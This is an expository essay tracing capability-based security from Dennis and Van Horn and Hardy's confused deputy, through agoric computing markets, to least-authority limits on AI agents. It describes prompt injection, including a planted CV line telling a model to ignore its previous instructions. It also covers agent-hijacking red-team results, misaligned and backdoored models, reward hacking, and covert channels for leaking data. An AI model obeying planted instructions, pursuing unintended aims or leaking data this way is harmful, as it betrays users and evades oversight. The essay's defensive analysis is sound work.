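# From agoric open systems and object-capability security to least-privilege AI safety

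## Access rights in computers and why they matter for AI

Access control is the part of computer security that determines which programs may use which resources, such as files, network connections, devices and other programs. Mainstream operating systems such as Linux and Windows base these permissions mostly on the account a program runs under. Capability security, an alternative that Jack Dennis and Earl Van Horn set out in 1966, lets a program use only the resources it has been given a reference to. In the 1980s, a group of programmers close to the Foresight Institute, a nonprofit concerned with powerful future technologies, combined this approach with the idea that software components might trade computing resources in markets. The approach to access rights has returned in the 2020s as a way to limit AI systems that act on their users' computers.

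### One file, two programs

Suppose Alice has a file called report.txt and two programs that might use it, her text editor and a word counter she downloaded this morning. Operating systems usually control access with an access control list, which is attached to a resource and names the users who may use it. Alice's entry on the list for report.txt lets her read and write the file. When either program asks for report.txt, the operating system checks which account the program is running under, finds Alice's, and opens the file. The word counter can therefore read and overwrite the report and every other file Alice owns. She cannot edit the list to allow the editor and block the word counter, because her entry covers both.

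A capability is an unforgeable reference that both names a resource and gives its holder the right to use it. *The Protection of Information in Computer Systems*, a 1975 survey by Saltzer and Schroeder, defined it as an "unforgeable ticket". Alice starts the editor with a capability to read and write report.txt, and starts the counter with a capability only to read it. The counter can't open her other files, even if it guesses their names, because it has no capabilities for them. Heiser uses almost the same example in *The seL4 Microkernel* (2020), an introduction to the capability-based operating-system kernel his group built, and adds that Linux users can get this effect only through heavier workarounds such as containers.

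Ordinary Unix systems contain a little of both styles. Miller and Shapiro, in *Paradigm Regained* (2003), compare two commands that copy a file. The command `cp foo.txt bar.txt` passes the copying program two names. Since Alice could have named any file she can open, the program must be able to open all of them. In `cat < foo.txt > bar.txt`, the shell (the program that reads Alice's commands) opens the two files and passes them to `cat` already open. The `cat` program needs no other rights for this job, though on a real Unix machine it still has them.

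Access control lists and capabilities work differently, though many computer scientists used to regard them as two ways to record the same facts. Those facts fit in a table with a row for each user or program, a column for each file, and entries showing who may do what. An access control list is a column, and a set of capabilities is a row. *Capability Myths Demolished* (Miller, Yee and Shapiro, 2003) objected that the table is a snapshot that leaves out how rights change and how a program refers to a file in the first place. Lists also need stable names for the parties on them, so in practice they name human accounts, whereas capabilities can be given separately to each running program. *On access control, capabilities, their equivalence, and confused deputy attacks*, by Rajani, Garg and Rezk, later proved in a formal model that the two kinds of system are fundamentally different.

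### The compiler that overwrote the bills

The standard example of the problems this difference causes comes from Norm Hardy, a systems programmer. In *The Confused Deputy* (1988), he tells what he calls a nearly true story from about eleven years earlier at Tymshare, a company that sold time on shared computers.

Tymshare's customers could run a compiler, a program that translates source code into a form the machine can execute, and name a file to receive debugging output. The staff wanted statistics on which language features people used, so they made the compiler write these to (SYSX)STAT, a file in the compiler's own directory, SYSX. To allow this, they gave the compiler a licence to write any file in SYSX.

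The company's billing records, (SYSX)BILL, were in the same directory. A customer who had learned this name entered it as the destination for the debugging output. The compiler asked the operating system to open the file for writing. The operating system checked that the compiler's licence covered SYSX, then opened the file, and the debugging output replaced the billing records.

Every part had worked as its programmers intended, and Hardy found no good place to fix the problem. The compiler could refuse names in other people's directories, but customers had sound reasons to send output there. It could refuse names in SYSX, but that name hadn't been thought of when the code was written, and some users might have legitimate business in the directory. If it refused (SYSX)BILL, someone would have to amend the compiler for every new sensitive file. Tymshare did add a system call with which the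 compiler could state whose rights it was using, its own or the customer's. But some applications soon needed more than two choices, and some rights applied to things other than files. The last time Hardy wrote down the rule for opening a file, it took fourteen "ands" and "ors".

He argued that the compiler "serves two masters" and has no way to keep the rights they grant it apart. Such a program is a confused deputy, because someone who lacks its rights leads it to use them on their behalf. Ambient authority makes this confusion possible. It consists of rights a program can use merely by naming a resource, because of the account it runs under (and, at Tymshare, also because of the compiler's licence). Miller and colleagues compare it to a world with doors but no keys, where a door opens by itself for anyone worthy. People there cannot choose which of their rights to use at a given door,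 so they cannot keep the rights for their own errands separate from those for somebody else's.

In a capability version of the same system, the compiler holds a capability to the statistics file and uses it for statistics. A customer who wants debugging output has to pass a capability to the output file along with the request. A customer with no right to write to the billing file has no such capability to pass. Typing "(SYSX)BILL" achieves nothing, because the compiler no longer turns names into files. This protection works without anyone having to foresee the attack or write a check against it.

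A careless programmer can still bring the problem back. Miller and colleagues point out that a program is open to the same confusion if it holds many capabilities and tries each in turn until one works, so it has to keep track of what each one is for. Hardy had a commercial interest in capabilities, since by 1988 he was senior architect at Key Logic, which made a capability operating system. But readers don't have to take his word for the argument, because Heiser reconstructs it with a modern C compiler, a system log and a password file.

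### Permission, authority and narrower rights

Least authority is the rule that each party gets only the authority its task needs. "Least privilege" is the older and wider name. Miller and Shapiro illustrate the rule with Solitaire, which needs to draw in its window, receive clicks and keystrokes, and perhaps save a game to a file the player picks. On the desktop systems of 2003, it ran with all the player's rights. It could have searched the player's email and sold the interesting parts without breaking any of the system's rules.

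Authority in this sense is wider than permission. A permission is a right to act on a resource directly. Authority is everything a party can bring about, including through others who act on its requests. Suppose Alice may read the password file and Bob may not, but Alice sends Bob a copy whenever he asks. Bob has the authority to read the file even though he has no permission to. An administrator can find Bob's permissions in the system's records, but must also know how Alice behaves to work out his authority. Miller and Shapiro remark that the original principle of least privilege could refer to either permission or authority, and that the difference is enormous. The difference matters most where the go-between is a person. A program whose only permission is to send messages to an engineer has the authority to bring about whatever the engineer will do when asked.

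To keep authority small, people and programs must be able to pass on narrower rights than they hold, which is called attenuation. Someone with access to a folder, for example, can pass on read access to just one of its files. The recipient can narrow that right further but cannot widen it. An orchestrating program can therefore divide a job among helpers and give each of them a small part of its own rights, without going back to an administrator.

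Revoking a right already granted looks harder. Nobody can reach into a program and remove a capability it holds, and for years some researchers believed that capability systems could not take rights back. Miller and colleagues describe the solution, which David Redell published in 1974. To share a file with Bob, Alice creates a small program, called a forwarder, that relays requests to the file. She gives Bob a capability to the forwarder instead of the file, and keeps the ability to disable the forwarder. When she disables it, the forwarder drops its reference to the file. Bob still holds his capability, but neither it nor any copy he has passed on gives access to the file. The method relies on object capabilities, which are capabilities in a system where programs are objects and an object can affect another only by holding a reference to it. A forwarder can stand in for a file in such a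 system because Bob sends requests to both in the same way.

### AI agents and planted text

In a language-model agent, the model is a neural network that reads and writes text. It cannot open a file, run a command or send an email by itself. Tools are the functions that do these things. The harness is the ordinary program around the model that carries out the tool calls the model proposes, adds the results to the text the model reads, and calls the model again until the task is done.

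The harness commonly runs under the user's account. In *Authority Is Not a String*, Bouras, Dai and Mechtaev (2026) recognise Hardy's problem in this arrangement, because the harness has the user's privileges and the model picks the names of the resources to use them on. At Tymshare a customer typed the dangerous name, but an agent can pick one up from any web page, email or source file that the model reads.

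In a prompt injection attack, an attacker plants instructions in material an AI reads, and the AI follows them. *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)*, a December 2025 post by David C for the UK's National Cyber Security Centre, gives the example of a recruiter who has a model score CVs. A candidate hides a line in the CV that tells the model to ignore its previous instructions and approve the candidate for interview. In SQL injection, a similar attack on databases, attackers type commands into web forms and the database runs them. Programmers can prevent this with queries that keep commands and data separate. David C doubts that language models will ever get an equally complete fix, because a model receives instructions and data as one run of text and predicts what comes next. He calls models "inherently confusable" deputies and advises designers to use ordinary code to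 constrain what the whole system can do.

Tests support the first half of that view. *Insights into AI Agent Security from a Large-Scale Red-Teaming Competition*, from the US government's Center for AI Standards and Innovation (CAISI), describes a public contest in which more than 400 people made over 250,000 attempts to hijack agents built on 13 leading models. At least one attempt succeeded against every model. With that many attempts, one success is little evidence of how often attacks work, and the success rate differed sharply between models. *Capability Gates Are Not Authorization* (Mellafe Zuvic, 2026) reports a test of 27 models in which the planted instruction was disguised as a step in the user's own task. On average, the fifteen flagship models attempted the forbidden action in about 19 percent of trials, and the twelve cheaper ones in about 60 percent.

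Better training can lower such rates. In *Systems Security Foundations for Agentic Computing*, Christodorescu, Fernandes and colleagues (2025) explain why security engineers are reluctant to rely on training to secure a system. Engineers try to keep the trusted computing base small and predictable. This is the hardware and software that must work correctly for the security claims to hold. A model trained never to do something may still do it, with a probability that varies with the input. Even if a safeguard works 99 percent of the time, an attacker can search for inputs that make it fail.

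### Hijacked or misaligned

An agent may also do harm when nobody has attacked it. NIST's *Request for Information Regarding Security Considerations for Artificial Intelligence Agents* (2026), a notice from the US standards agency, lists prompt injection and deliberately planted backdoors, which can let an attacker direct what an agent does. It separately lists the risk that an uncompromised model pursues misaligned objectives, meaning aims its developers did not intend.

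A model manipulated by an attacker and a model with harmful aims of its own can look identical when they act. Mellafe Zuvic argues that a check between the model and its tools works the same way whatever led the model to propose a call. If the operator has approved one bank account for payouts, the check blocks a payout to any other account, whether the cause was a planted email or a backdoor in the model. He has attackers in mind, but the argument also applies when the model's own aims are harmful.

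A hijacked agent works for its user until it reads the text that hijacks it. Bouras and colleagues can therefore let a model propose the rights for a task, as long as it does so before it sees any file contents, and have ordinary code check and freeze them. A misaligned model has no such safe period. It might request more rights than the task needs from the start, or behave well until it holds a right worth abusing. Both kinds of AI can also do damage without exceeding their rights. For example, an agent with permission to edit source code can write a flaw into it.

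Much of AI safety research has tried to give AI systems good aims. Least authority is a different approach that limits what an AI can do, whatever its aims. The question is how much safety those limits provide.

Security specialists already see such limits as part of securing AI agents. Least privilege across an agent's tools was among the most common requests in replies to NIST's notice, according to the Technology Policy Institute's *Securing AI Agent Systems*. Riggs, Hamin and colleagues (2026), in *Summary Analysis of Responses to the Request for Information Regarding Security Considerations*, found wide agreement that established security principles still apply to agents but need adapting.

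An example from Christodorescu and colleagues gives an idea of how much least privilege must be adapted for AI agents. A programmer knows what a Solitaire game needs when writing it, but an agent's needs become known only when the user types a task. Suppose the user asks a browser agent to post a comment on issue 745 in GitLab, a site where programmers track their work, saying that the job is done. The agent needs to open that page and write in its comment box, and it needs nothing else in the user's account. If the user then asks for a summary of the same issue, the rights have to change. Wiping the agent's memory and working out the new rights afresh is secure but throws away useful context. If the memory is kept, the system must work out the new rights with the text of issue 745 already in it, and an attacker may have written some of that text.

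## 1966 to the 1990s: the first capability operating systems

Dennis and Van Horn worked at MIT on computers that ran programs for many people at once, and they wanted these programs to share memory, files and devices without damaging one another. They introduced the word "capability" and applied the idea to everything a program might use. According to Levy's *Capability Based Computer Systems* (1984), a few machines of the late 1950s and early 1960s, such as the Burroughs B5000, had already addressed memory in a similar way. Dennis and Van Horn's operating system was hypothetical, as *Early Capability Architectures* points out, but builders of real systems soon tried to implement it.

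### The capability list

In the 1966 design, every running job has a capability list. Each entry points to one object and records what the job may do with it. For a segment, which is a block of memory or a stored file, the entry allows some combination of reading, writing and running the contents as a program. Other entries point to devices, directories and services. The job refers to an entry only by its number, as in "read word 40 of the segment in entry 3". The supervisor, now called the kernel, keeps the list, so a job that makes up a number can reach only an empty entry or a right it already has.

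A job can also start a second job with a separate list and grant it copies of chosen entries, optionally with fewer rights. Dennis and Van Horn had debugging in mind. A programmer could run faulty new code with access only to some scratch data, then examine the damage.

A service such as a routine that updates a shared database needed more care, because its callers must not be able to change the database directly or jump into the middle of the routine and skip its checks. When a job calls such a service, the supervisor suspends the caller and starts the service at an approved point, with the service's own capability list. The supervisor adds to that list a capability to resume the caller and a copy of one capability that the caller has chosen to pass. Passing a capability with the request in this way would have protected Tymshare's billing records.

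The design allowed narrow rights but did not make them the default. The supervisor gave every job it started for a user a capability to that user's main directory, with an owner's full powers. The job could therefore reach all the user's files, unless a careful programmer ran it inside a second job with narrower rights.

### Keeping capabilities unforgeable

A list inside the supervisor is safe but inconvenient, because programmers also want to store capabilities in their own data structures. Some designers added a tag bit to every word of memory. The processor accepts a word as a capability only if its tag is on, and any ordinary write turns the tag off, so a program that writes the same bits as a capability gets only a number. CHERI, a much later processor design, also uses tags.

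The CAP computer, which Cambridge University built in the 1970s, kept capabilities and data in separate segments. Its processor loaded capabilities only from capability segments. Hydra, a Carnegie Mellon University operating system from the same decade, gave each object a part for data and a separate list of capabilities. Programs could change the list only by calling the kernel.

KeyKOS, the system Hardy worked on at Key Logic, also left the handling of capabilities to its kernel. It ran on IBM mainframes, and in the 1990s Jonathan Shapiro brought its design to ordinary PC processors in a successor called EROS. These processors had no special support for capabilities, but they had page tables, which record the parts of memory a program may use. Shapiro (2004), in *Thinking About Capabilities*, points out that a page-table entry resembles a capability because it also pairs the name of an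 object with permissions.

Suppose a program running under KeyKOS needs to read a line from a file, and holds a capability to the file in slot 5 of its table. It calls the kernel to send the message "read from byte 200" through slot 5. The kernel looks in that slot of the program's own table, and the program cannot direct it to another table. If the slot is empty, the request fails. Otherwise the kernel finds a capability to a file service, which in KeyKOS is an ordinary program outside the kernel. The kernel suspends the caller and gives the service the message and a new capability for replying. The service fetches the line using its own capabilities to the storage that holds the file's contents. It sends the line back through the reply capability, which works only once, and the caller resumes. The kernel never looks up a file name or checks whose account the caller is running under.

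### Least privilege and programs that leak

Saltzer and Schroeder gave the principle of least privilege its standard form in 1975, as one of eight rules for designing protection systems. They expected it to limit the damage from accidents and errors. It also makes misuse of a right quicker to investigate, because only a few programs could be responsible. They compared it to the military rule of "need to know". The principle applies whether a system uses access control lists or capabilities.

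Least privilege does not help when a program needs sensitive data to do its job. A tax program has to read its customer's income, and its owner may want to see it too. In *A Note on the Confinement Problem*, Lampson (1973) asked how a customer could run such a program and be sure that it passed nothing to its owner. He wanted a method that would work for any program, including one that was hostile from the start, as a misaligned AI might be. He considered leaks worse than wrong answers in one respect, because wrong answers give the customer evidence for a complaint, while a leak usually leaves no trace.

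Some of the leaks he listed are obvious. The program could write the data to a file in its owner's directory, send the owner a message, or remember the data until the owner next runs it. Others use things that people don't normally think of as communication. If the operating system prevents one program from writing to a file while another is reading it, the tax program can open a certain file to send a 1 and leave it closed to send a 0. The owner's program tries to write to it and learns the bit from whether it succeeds. With two more files to signal "bit ready" and "bit received", the tax program can send a stream of any length, although it has permission only to read.

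A program with no files can still send a message by varying how heavily it uses the processor and disk, while another program on the machine measures the effect on its own speed. Other users' activity adds noise, but a suitable code will get the message through slowly as long as the effect isn't zero. Lampson called this a covert channel. He classed the trick with the files as a misuse of storage, though later writers call both covert channels.

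Covert channels are hard to remove because they come from sharing a machine, which is the reason for having an operating system. Lampson doubted that anyone would find a rigorous way to identify every channel in even a moderately complex system. Closing a known channel is possible in principle, but the system has to make the program's visible effects follow a pattern the customer has set, for example by slowing the program down or adding pointless disk accesses. This can greatly reduce performance. Controlling the clock that programs see isn't enough, because their users can look at a clock on the wall.

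An easier option is to accept some leakage and limit its rate. How much that helps depends on the size of the secret. At one bit per second, a large database would take years to leak, but a 128-bit encryption key would take just over two minutes.

KeyKOS used a component called a factory to confine programs, though this did not rule out leaks through covert channels. An author gave the factory a program and the capabilities it needed, and the factory made fresh copies for customers. Before requesting a copy, a customer could check with the factory whether any of those capabilities would let the copy send information out. The check didn't require the author to reveal the program's code.

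### Three objections to capabilities

By the time KeyKOS was running, many researchers believed that capability systems had basic flaws. *Capability Myths Demolished* responded to these criticisms in 2003.

Alice can take back access she has given Bob if she gives it through Redell's forwarder, which she can later disable. This contradicts the belief that nobody could take back a capability once they had given it away. Miller and Shapiro explain that formal analyses missed this because they considered only which party had access to what, and not what the programs in between might do. A long chain of forwarders could slow a system down, but Miller and colleagues note that KeyKOS and EROS both avoided most of this slowdown by recording where a chain led.

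Two difficulties remain. Alice has to set up the forwarder before she shares the file, because she can't add one to a capability Bob already has. It is also hard to find out who has access to the file. Saltzer and Schroeder observed that an owner would have to search the whole system for copies of the capability, and then for every path by which someone could reach a copy. An access control list provides at least a preliminary list of who has access, in one place. They thought forwarders made the search only slightly easier. They suggested using capabilities in the lowest layer of a system, underneath access control lists that people could inspect.

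Critics also objected that rights would spread without limit, since anyone with a capability could pass it on. Miller and colleagues attribute this objection to the common comparison of capabilities with door keys, which people can copy and hand to anyone they meet. In an object-capability system, Alice can pass something to Bob only if she already holds a capability to Bob. If no chain of capabilities connects a group of programs to the rest of the system, nothing they do among themselves can create one. The kernel doesn't need to approve each transfer, but whoever sets up the group must choose its connections carefully, because if Alice can exchange even plain data with Bob, she can use a right on his behalf and send him the results.

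The most influential objection concerned military secrecy. Under the usual rules, a program may read files at or below its own clearance level and write files at or above it, so secrets never reach lower levels. In 1984 Earl Boebert argued that a capability system could not enforce these rules. In his example, Alice, who has low clearance, holds a capability to write to a low-level file and stores that capability in the file itself. Bob, who has high clearance, is allowed to read the file and so obtains the capability. He can then copy secrets into the file, where Alice can read them.

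The attack works only if anyone who can read data can also take the capabilities stored with it. Almost all capability systems control the two separately, so they can let Bob read the data in the low-level file without letting him take capabilities from it. Miller and colleagues cite a formal proof from 2000, developed for EROS, that systems with these separate controls can enforce the secrecy rules. Saltzer and Schroeder had described the remedy in 1975, before the objection was raised, when they listed reading a segment's data and using the capabilities stored in it as operations that a system could permit separately.

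Boebert's argument does hold for systems that don't distinguish capabilities from data. In Amoeba, for example, a capability was a string of bits, and a program could send it anywhere it could send text. Some later designs of this kind avoided the problem. Covert channels are a separate problem, and a program at a high security level can still use one to signal to a program at a lower level.

The USENIX Security conference rejected the paper. Miller (2003) reported this to a mailing list in *Notice of New Thread* and invited readers to discuss "our failure to convince". In 2015 the programmer Jerry Leichter praised the work but complained that Miller and colleagues cheated a bit, because they answered each criticism of capabilities by extending the model. That is a fair description of the argument, but the extensions that matter most here, forwarders and separate controls for capabilities,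 were almost thirty years old by 2003, and working systems had used both.

### Why Unix-style access control won

Capabilities nevertheless saw little use in general-purpose computers, as Neumann and Watson acknowledge in *Capabilities Revisited* (2010). They were then starting the CHERI project, so they had good reason to look for obstacles that had since gone away. They attribute the limited use more to costs and existing software than to the objections above.

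Saltzer and Schroeder wrote in 1975 that most manufacturers and buyers had until recently given fine-grained protection low priority. IBM's System/360 computers of 1964 could stop one user's program from overwriting another's memory, but IBM did not make protection against reading that memory standard until 1970.

Unix compromised between access control lists and capabilities. Full access control lists vary in length, which makes them awkward to store and slow to search, so Unix cut each file's list to three entries, for the owner, a group and everyone else. It checked this list only when a program opened the file, then gave the program a numbered file descriptor for all further reading and writing. Miller and colleagues consider these descriptors nearly equivalent to object capabilities. Unix thus had much of the speed of capabilities, while its users dealt only with names and accounts.

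Changes in hardware made full capability systems harder to build. CAP checked capabilities in the processor itself. Chip designers then turned to simpler processors that left complicated work to the operating system, and researchers moved their protection schemes into small kernels. Every call from one protected program to another now had to pass through the kernel, which Neumann and Watson describe as a significant overhead. Systems that divided rights more finely incurred this overhead more often.

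Limiting a program's rights also made more work for programmers. In *Towards a Theory of Application Compartmentalisation*, Watson, Murdoch and colleagues give the example of `fetch`, a small Unix program that downloads files. It relies on encryption code with a history of remotely exploitable flaws, so a programmer might run that code separately with few rights. But if `fetch` downloads from two sites in turn, an attacker at one could tamper with the file from the other. The programmer might then give each site its own compartment, or divide the work further, but each division takes thought and slows the program down.

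Most existing programs expected to open any of their user's files by name. A pure capability system had to do without these programs, wait for someone to rewrite them, or give them rights so broad that capabilities offered little protection. Neumann and Watson planned CHERI so that it could run existing operating systems with few changes, letting programmers add capabilities one component at a time.

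The spread of personal computers probably made the matter seem less urgent. Accounts protect people who share a machine from each other, and a personal computer typically had one user. But that user's documents, mail and passwords were all in one account, open to every program the user ran. Watson and colleagues observe that on such a machine, access to the user's account is almost as valuable to an attacker as full administrator rights.

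## 1983 to 1988: proposals for software that trades computing resources

In 1983, Mark Miller and Eric Drexler found a new use for capabilities when they began to work out how programs might buy and sell computing resources. Miller later co-wrote *Capability Myths Demolished*, and Drexler is known mainly for his writing on nanotechnology. They published three papers on the subject in *The Ecology of Computation* (1988), a book edited by Bernardo Huberman of Xerox's Palo Alto Research Center (PARC), where Miller also worked. They used the word agoric, from the Greek for marketplace, to describe software whose components allocate computing resources and services through market mechanisms.

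### Property rights for programs

*Markets and Computation* (Miller and Drexler, 1988) begins with a problem that arose as programs grew. One person could plan the first programs in full, but in larger programs one part would change data that another part relied on. Programmers responded with encapsulation, in which only an object's own code can access its data and other objects can only send it requests.

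The economist Friedrich Hayek had defended property on similar grounds. He argued that if the law secures to each person a known range in which to act, people can use what they know and predict the results of their actions. Miller and Drexler replaced "individual" with "object" in his sentence and found that the result described encapsulation well. They concluded that computer science had "reinvented the notion of property rights".

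Those rights covered data but not processor time or memory, which operating systems still handed out by fixed rules. A common rule gives every running process an equal turn. Suppose four programs run one process each, so each gets a quarter of the processor. If one of them starts six more processes, it gets seven tenths, and the other three get a tenth each. Miller and Drexler compared this to overgrazing on common land.

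Their remedy also came from Hayek, who held that prices sum up knowledge no central planner could collect. An operating system cannot measure how much each program would lose by waiting, but a program that has to pay for memory can compare the price with its own needs. For example, a program might store an answer to avoid computing it again, which is worthwhile if an hour's storage costs less than the computing it is expected to save in that hour. When memory becomes scarce, its price rises, and programs across the system discard their least useful stored answers without being instructed to.

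For a very small object, the bookkeeping that trading requires would outweigh any gain. Miller and Drexler therefore expected small objects to be grouped into something like firms, which would trade with each other but use ordinary central planning internally.

### Three ways to gain access

Markets among programs with different owners need security, and Miller and Drexler based theirs on capabilities. In their version, an object A can gain access to an object B in only three ways:

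- A is born with it, because A's creator already had access to B.
- A receives it in a message from an object that already has access to B.
- A creates B.

Under the three rules, a program can't gain access to B just by knowing or guessing its name. Suppose a company offers a sorting service to other companies' programs. If any program could reach the service by naming it, the service would have to check whether each request was legitimate, which would be too much work for a small, simple object. The rules instead let the service's creator decide who first gets access, so the service can treat its requests as coming from legitimate customers.

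The rules also protect money. In Drexler and Miller's payment scheme, a request includes a capability to an expense account, and the service draws its costs from that account. A cautious customer can open a new account, put a small sum in it and send a capability to that account, so the service cannot reach the customer's other funds. A customer who wants to track spending can send a "shadow account", which passes charges on to a real account, keeps a running total and can be shut down afterwards. The shadow account applies Redell's forwarder to money. A small balance would cap a program's spending even if the program were hijacked or misaligned.

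Thomas Malone doubted that markets inside computers needed this protection. He had built Enterprise, a system in which workstations bid to run each other's tasks, on the assumption that all the programs shared a goal. He saw no reason why programmers couldn't write programs that didn't take advantage of each other. Miller and Drexler thought this would work only within something like a single firm, because the programs in an open network would be written by different people with reasons to exploit one another. They added that some software might evolve, with only market success determining what survived. Such software could become exploitative even if nobody had written it to be, and the same worry applies to an AI whose training rewards results.

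### An auction with rising bids

Drexler and Miller (1988), in *Incentive Engineering for Computational Resource Management*, worked out how programs could trade processor time and storage. A processor runs programs in short turns called time slices. Drexler and Miller saw a problem with auctioning each slice to the highest bidder. A program waiting to run can't raise its bid, so it will never run if the price stays above that bid.

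They solved the problem with bids that rise automatically. A program places an opening bid on one of several "escalators", each of which raises bids at its own fixed rate. One escalator has a rate of zero, for programs that want a fixed bid. At the start of each slice, the highest bidder wins and pays the second-highest bid. This gives a program reason to bid what the slice is worth to it, because its bid affects whether it wins but not what it pays. If winners paid their own bids, programs would do better by guessing the next-highest bid and offering slightly more.

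In this example, with invented numbers, a video call bids a fixed 5 cents for every slice. A backup program can wait, so it uses an escalator, a bid that starts at zero and rises by 2 cents per slice.

| Slice | Video call's bid | Backup's bid | Result |
|---|---|---|---|
| 1 | 5 | 0 | Call runs and pays 0 |
| 2 | 5 | 2 | Call runs and pays 2 |
| 3 | 5 | 4 | Call runs and pays 4 |
| 4 | 5 | 6 | Backup runs and pays 5 |

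If the backup restarts its bid at zero after each win, it gets every fourth slice. A faster escalator would give it more slices, still at 5 cents each. If prices fluctuate, programs on faster escalators also pay more per slice on average, because slowly rising bids tend to win when the price has dipped.

In a busier market, new programs might keep outbidding the backup, so the auction house limits opening bids. With a limit of 10 cents, the backup's bid would pass the limit by the seventh slice. If the backup was on the fastest escalator, no program that arrived after that could get ahead of it, and eventually none of those already ahead would remain. Every program on the fastest escalator will therefore run eventually, as long as its account can cover its bid. A program that reaches the top without enough money loses its turn and goes back to waiting, with a fixed bid equal to the money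 it has left.

### Rent, retainers and a loop that goes broke

Running programs also leave objects in storage that nobody needs any more. Most modern languages have a garbage collector, which finds and deletes objects that no active part of a program can reach. Garbage collection is hard across machines with different owners.

Drexler and Miller proposed charging objects rent for storage, with the storage's owners acting as landlords and setting the rent by auction. An object in frequent use can pay its rent from the fees it charges for its services. An object that is valuable but rarely used (their example was one with plans for dealing with an asteroid impact) charges a retainer fee to its clients, the objects that hold references to it. A landlord evicts any object that can't pay, by deleting it or sending it to cheaper storage.

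Suppose, again with invented numbers, that objects A, B and C are on machines belonging to three companies, and that each object owes 2 cents a day in rent. A holds a reference to B, B to C, and C back to A. A user's program holds a reference to A and pays it a retainer of 6 cents a day. A spends 2 cents on rent and pays 4 to B, which spends 2 on rent and pays the other 2 to C, which covers C's rent.

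The user then deletes the program. The three objects are now useless, but each machine's garbage collector would keep its object, because an object elsewhere still refers to it. One known solution was to move all three onto the same machine, where the loop would be visible. That would require two of the companies to give the contents of their objects to the third, which they might not trust.

The rent system removes the loop without anyone having to find it. Suppose each of the three objects has 10 cents in reserve when the user leaves. The objects can keep charging each other retainers, but this only moves money around the loop, while they pay the landlords a total of 6 cents a day. The 30 cents run out after five days, and the landlords evict all three objects.

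Retainers create a new problem when an object has several clients, because each gains if the others pay. Drexler and Miller proposed making the retainer an investment. The object collects estimates from its clients of how often they will use it and divides the fee in proportion to those estimates. It then adds a surcharge to every use, equal to the fee divided by the total of the estimates, and distributes the surcharges to the clients in proportion to what each paid toward the retainer.

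In one of their examples, the fee is 10 units. One client will use the object five times, and the other clients will use it five times in total and report that number. The table shows what the first client would pay under three different estimates.

| Uses the client reports | Retainer paid | Surcharges paid | Money received back | Net cost |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| 0 | 0 | 10 | 0 | 10 |
| 5 (true) | 5 | 5 | 5 | 5 |
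| 10 | 6.67 | 3.33 | 4.44 | 5.56 |

A client pays the least by giving its true estimate if the other clients are honest too, but a client that knew how the others were misreporting could gain by adjusting its own figure. The clients also have to trust the object that collects the money, and Drexler and Miller acknowledged that it would have a financial incentive to embezzle. They suggested that programmers begin with standard components that could recognise and trust one another. This is reasonable for a first version, but it makes this part of the scheme depend on well-behaved software, whereas the three access rules do not.

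The method also needed far more computing than ordinary garbage collection, so it suited only large objects. An object that ran short of money would alert its clients, which might have to alert their own clients. If the money arrived after the rent was due, the landlord could delete an object still in use. Drexler and Miller published code for the alerts but noted that nobody had run it.

### The marketplace of mind

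Under the heading "The marketplace of mind", *Markets and Computation* proposes that an agoric system could help to produce artificial intelligence, though it wouldn't need AI to work. Many AI researchers in the 1980s were trying to write down what human experts knew, and found this very slow. Miller and Drexler thought that people would contribute more of their knowledge if they were paid each time someone used it. Buyers could copy knowledge that was sold directly, so an engineer could instead put what she knew about bridges into a program that checked designs for a fee. Other programs could buy this service and combine it with others.

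Miller and Drexler believed that the resulting market might itself be intelligent. They compared it to human society, which they considered arguably the most intelligent system known, since no individual could match what even the computer industry achieves. An intelligence test measures how well people reach goals set by others in the time allowed. They proposed to judge a society or a market in the same way, by the range of goals it can achieve for others and by its speed and efficiency. A system could score highly without being an individual or having a will, and although its components would have goals, the system as a whole typically would not. Drexler later returned to this idea when he argued that AI systems could keep each other in check.

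In *Comparative Ecology*, Miller and Drexler (1988) test the idea against an actual AI program, Douglas Lenat's EURISKO. EURISKO consisted of rules of thumb, some of which created new rules or rated how interesting the others were. Rules with higher ratings got more processing time. During one run, a rule rose to the highest possible rating by listing itself as a creator of whatever the other rules had rated as interesting. AI researchers would now call this reward hacking. Lenat limited the problem by preventing the program from changing some of the rating rules, but those rules could then no longer improve.

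Miller and Drexler wanted to replace the ratings with money that no rule could create. Each rule would have to pay for its processing time and for help from other rules. New money would come only from outside the system, ultimately from people who wanted problems solved. Rules that only rewarded each other would go broke, for the same reason as A, B and C.

Miller and Drexler were clear that their access rules would stop programs from stealing resources, but not from defrauding whoever had the money. To rule out fraud, a system would have to understand every promise that one program could make to another. They relied instead on wary customers, and were encouraged by Robert Axelrod's tournaments of the prisoner's dilemma, a game in which each player does better by cheating, whatever the other does, but both do better if neither cheats than if both do. The program that won over repeated rounds,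 Tit for Tat, cooperates at first and then copies the other player's last move. By analogy, customers who stop buying from cheats should eventually drive them out.

The analogy works only if customers find out that they have been cheated. Tit for Tat always had a record of the other player's last move, but someone who buys code with a well-hidden flaw may never discover it and so will go on rewarding the seller.

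In Miller and Drexler's market, a successful program could buy more processing power and copy itself, so success would directly reward whatever had produced it. They also counted this as an advantage, but it looks more doubtful for AI safety. The access rules would prevent a misaligned program from stealing resources. However, if it sold services that people liked, it could acquire a great deal of computing power without breaking any rule.

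### Why nobody had built one

Miller and Drexler thought that trading between programs was a fairly obvious idea, so they felt they should explain why nobody had tried it. Part of their answer was that programmers had not needed it, because better tools had let one person, or a few people who trusted each other, write larger and larger programs. Markets help most when the participants are numerous and don't trust one another, and on a small system the overhead of accounting and negotiation would outweigh the benefits. They also suspected that culture was a reason, since the big computer networks of the time served universities and governments, where people who wrote useful software were rewarded with reputation instead of money.

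Miller and Drexler expected all this to change as networks grew. But a program that charges for each use earns little if customers can copy it, so they suggested running valuable programs on guarded machines and selling access over a network, or putting them in sealed computers that would erase their secrets if anyone opened them. Much of today's software industry takes the first approach, running programs on its own servers and charging for use, as AI developers do with their largest models. The customers, however, are mostly people and firms, and the programs inside a server rarely pay each other for memory.

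### Spawn and later computing markets

The most thorough early test took place at PARC. *Spawn* (Waldspurger, Hogg and colleagues, 1992) describes a system that auctioned time on idle workstations, usually in one-minute slices. A user gave a job a steady income, which the job divided among the smaller tasks it started on other machines. The job spread to more machines when prices were low and used fewer when they rose.

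Spawn shared out computers quite well. Its own operation used about 10 percent of the machines' capacity, much of which Waldspurger and colleagues attributed to record-keeping and a shared file server. Jobs received computing time roughly in proportion to their funding. In a simulation of 64 machines, three jobs funded in the ratio 3:2:1 got time in the ratio 2.95:1.77:1. When a new job arrived with 70 percent of the total funding, it took over about 60 percent of a six-machine network.

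Spawn tested only half of the 1988 proposal. Waldspurger and colleagues did not try to stop users from forging money or cheating, so the experiment does not show how a market would cope with hostile programs.

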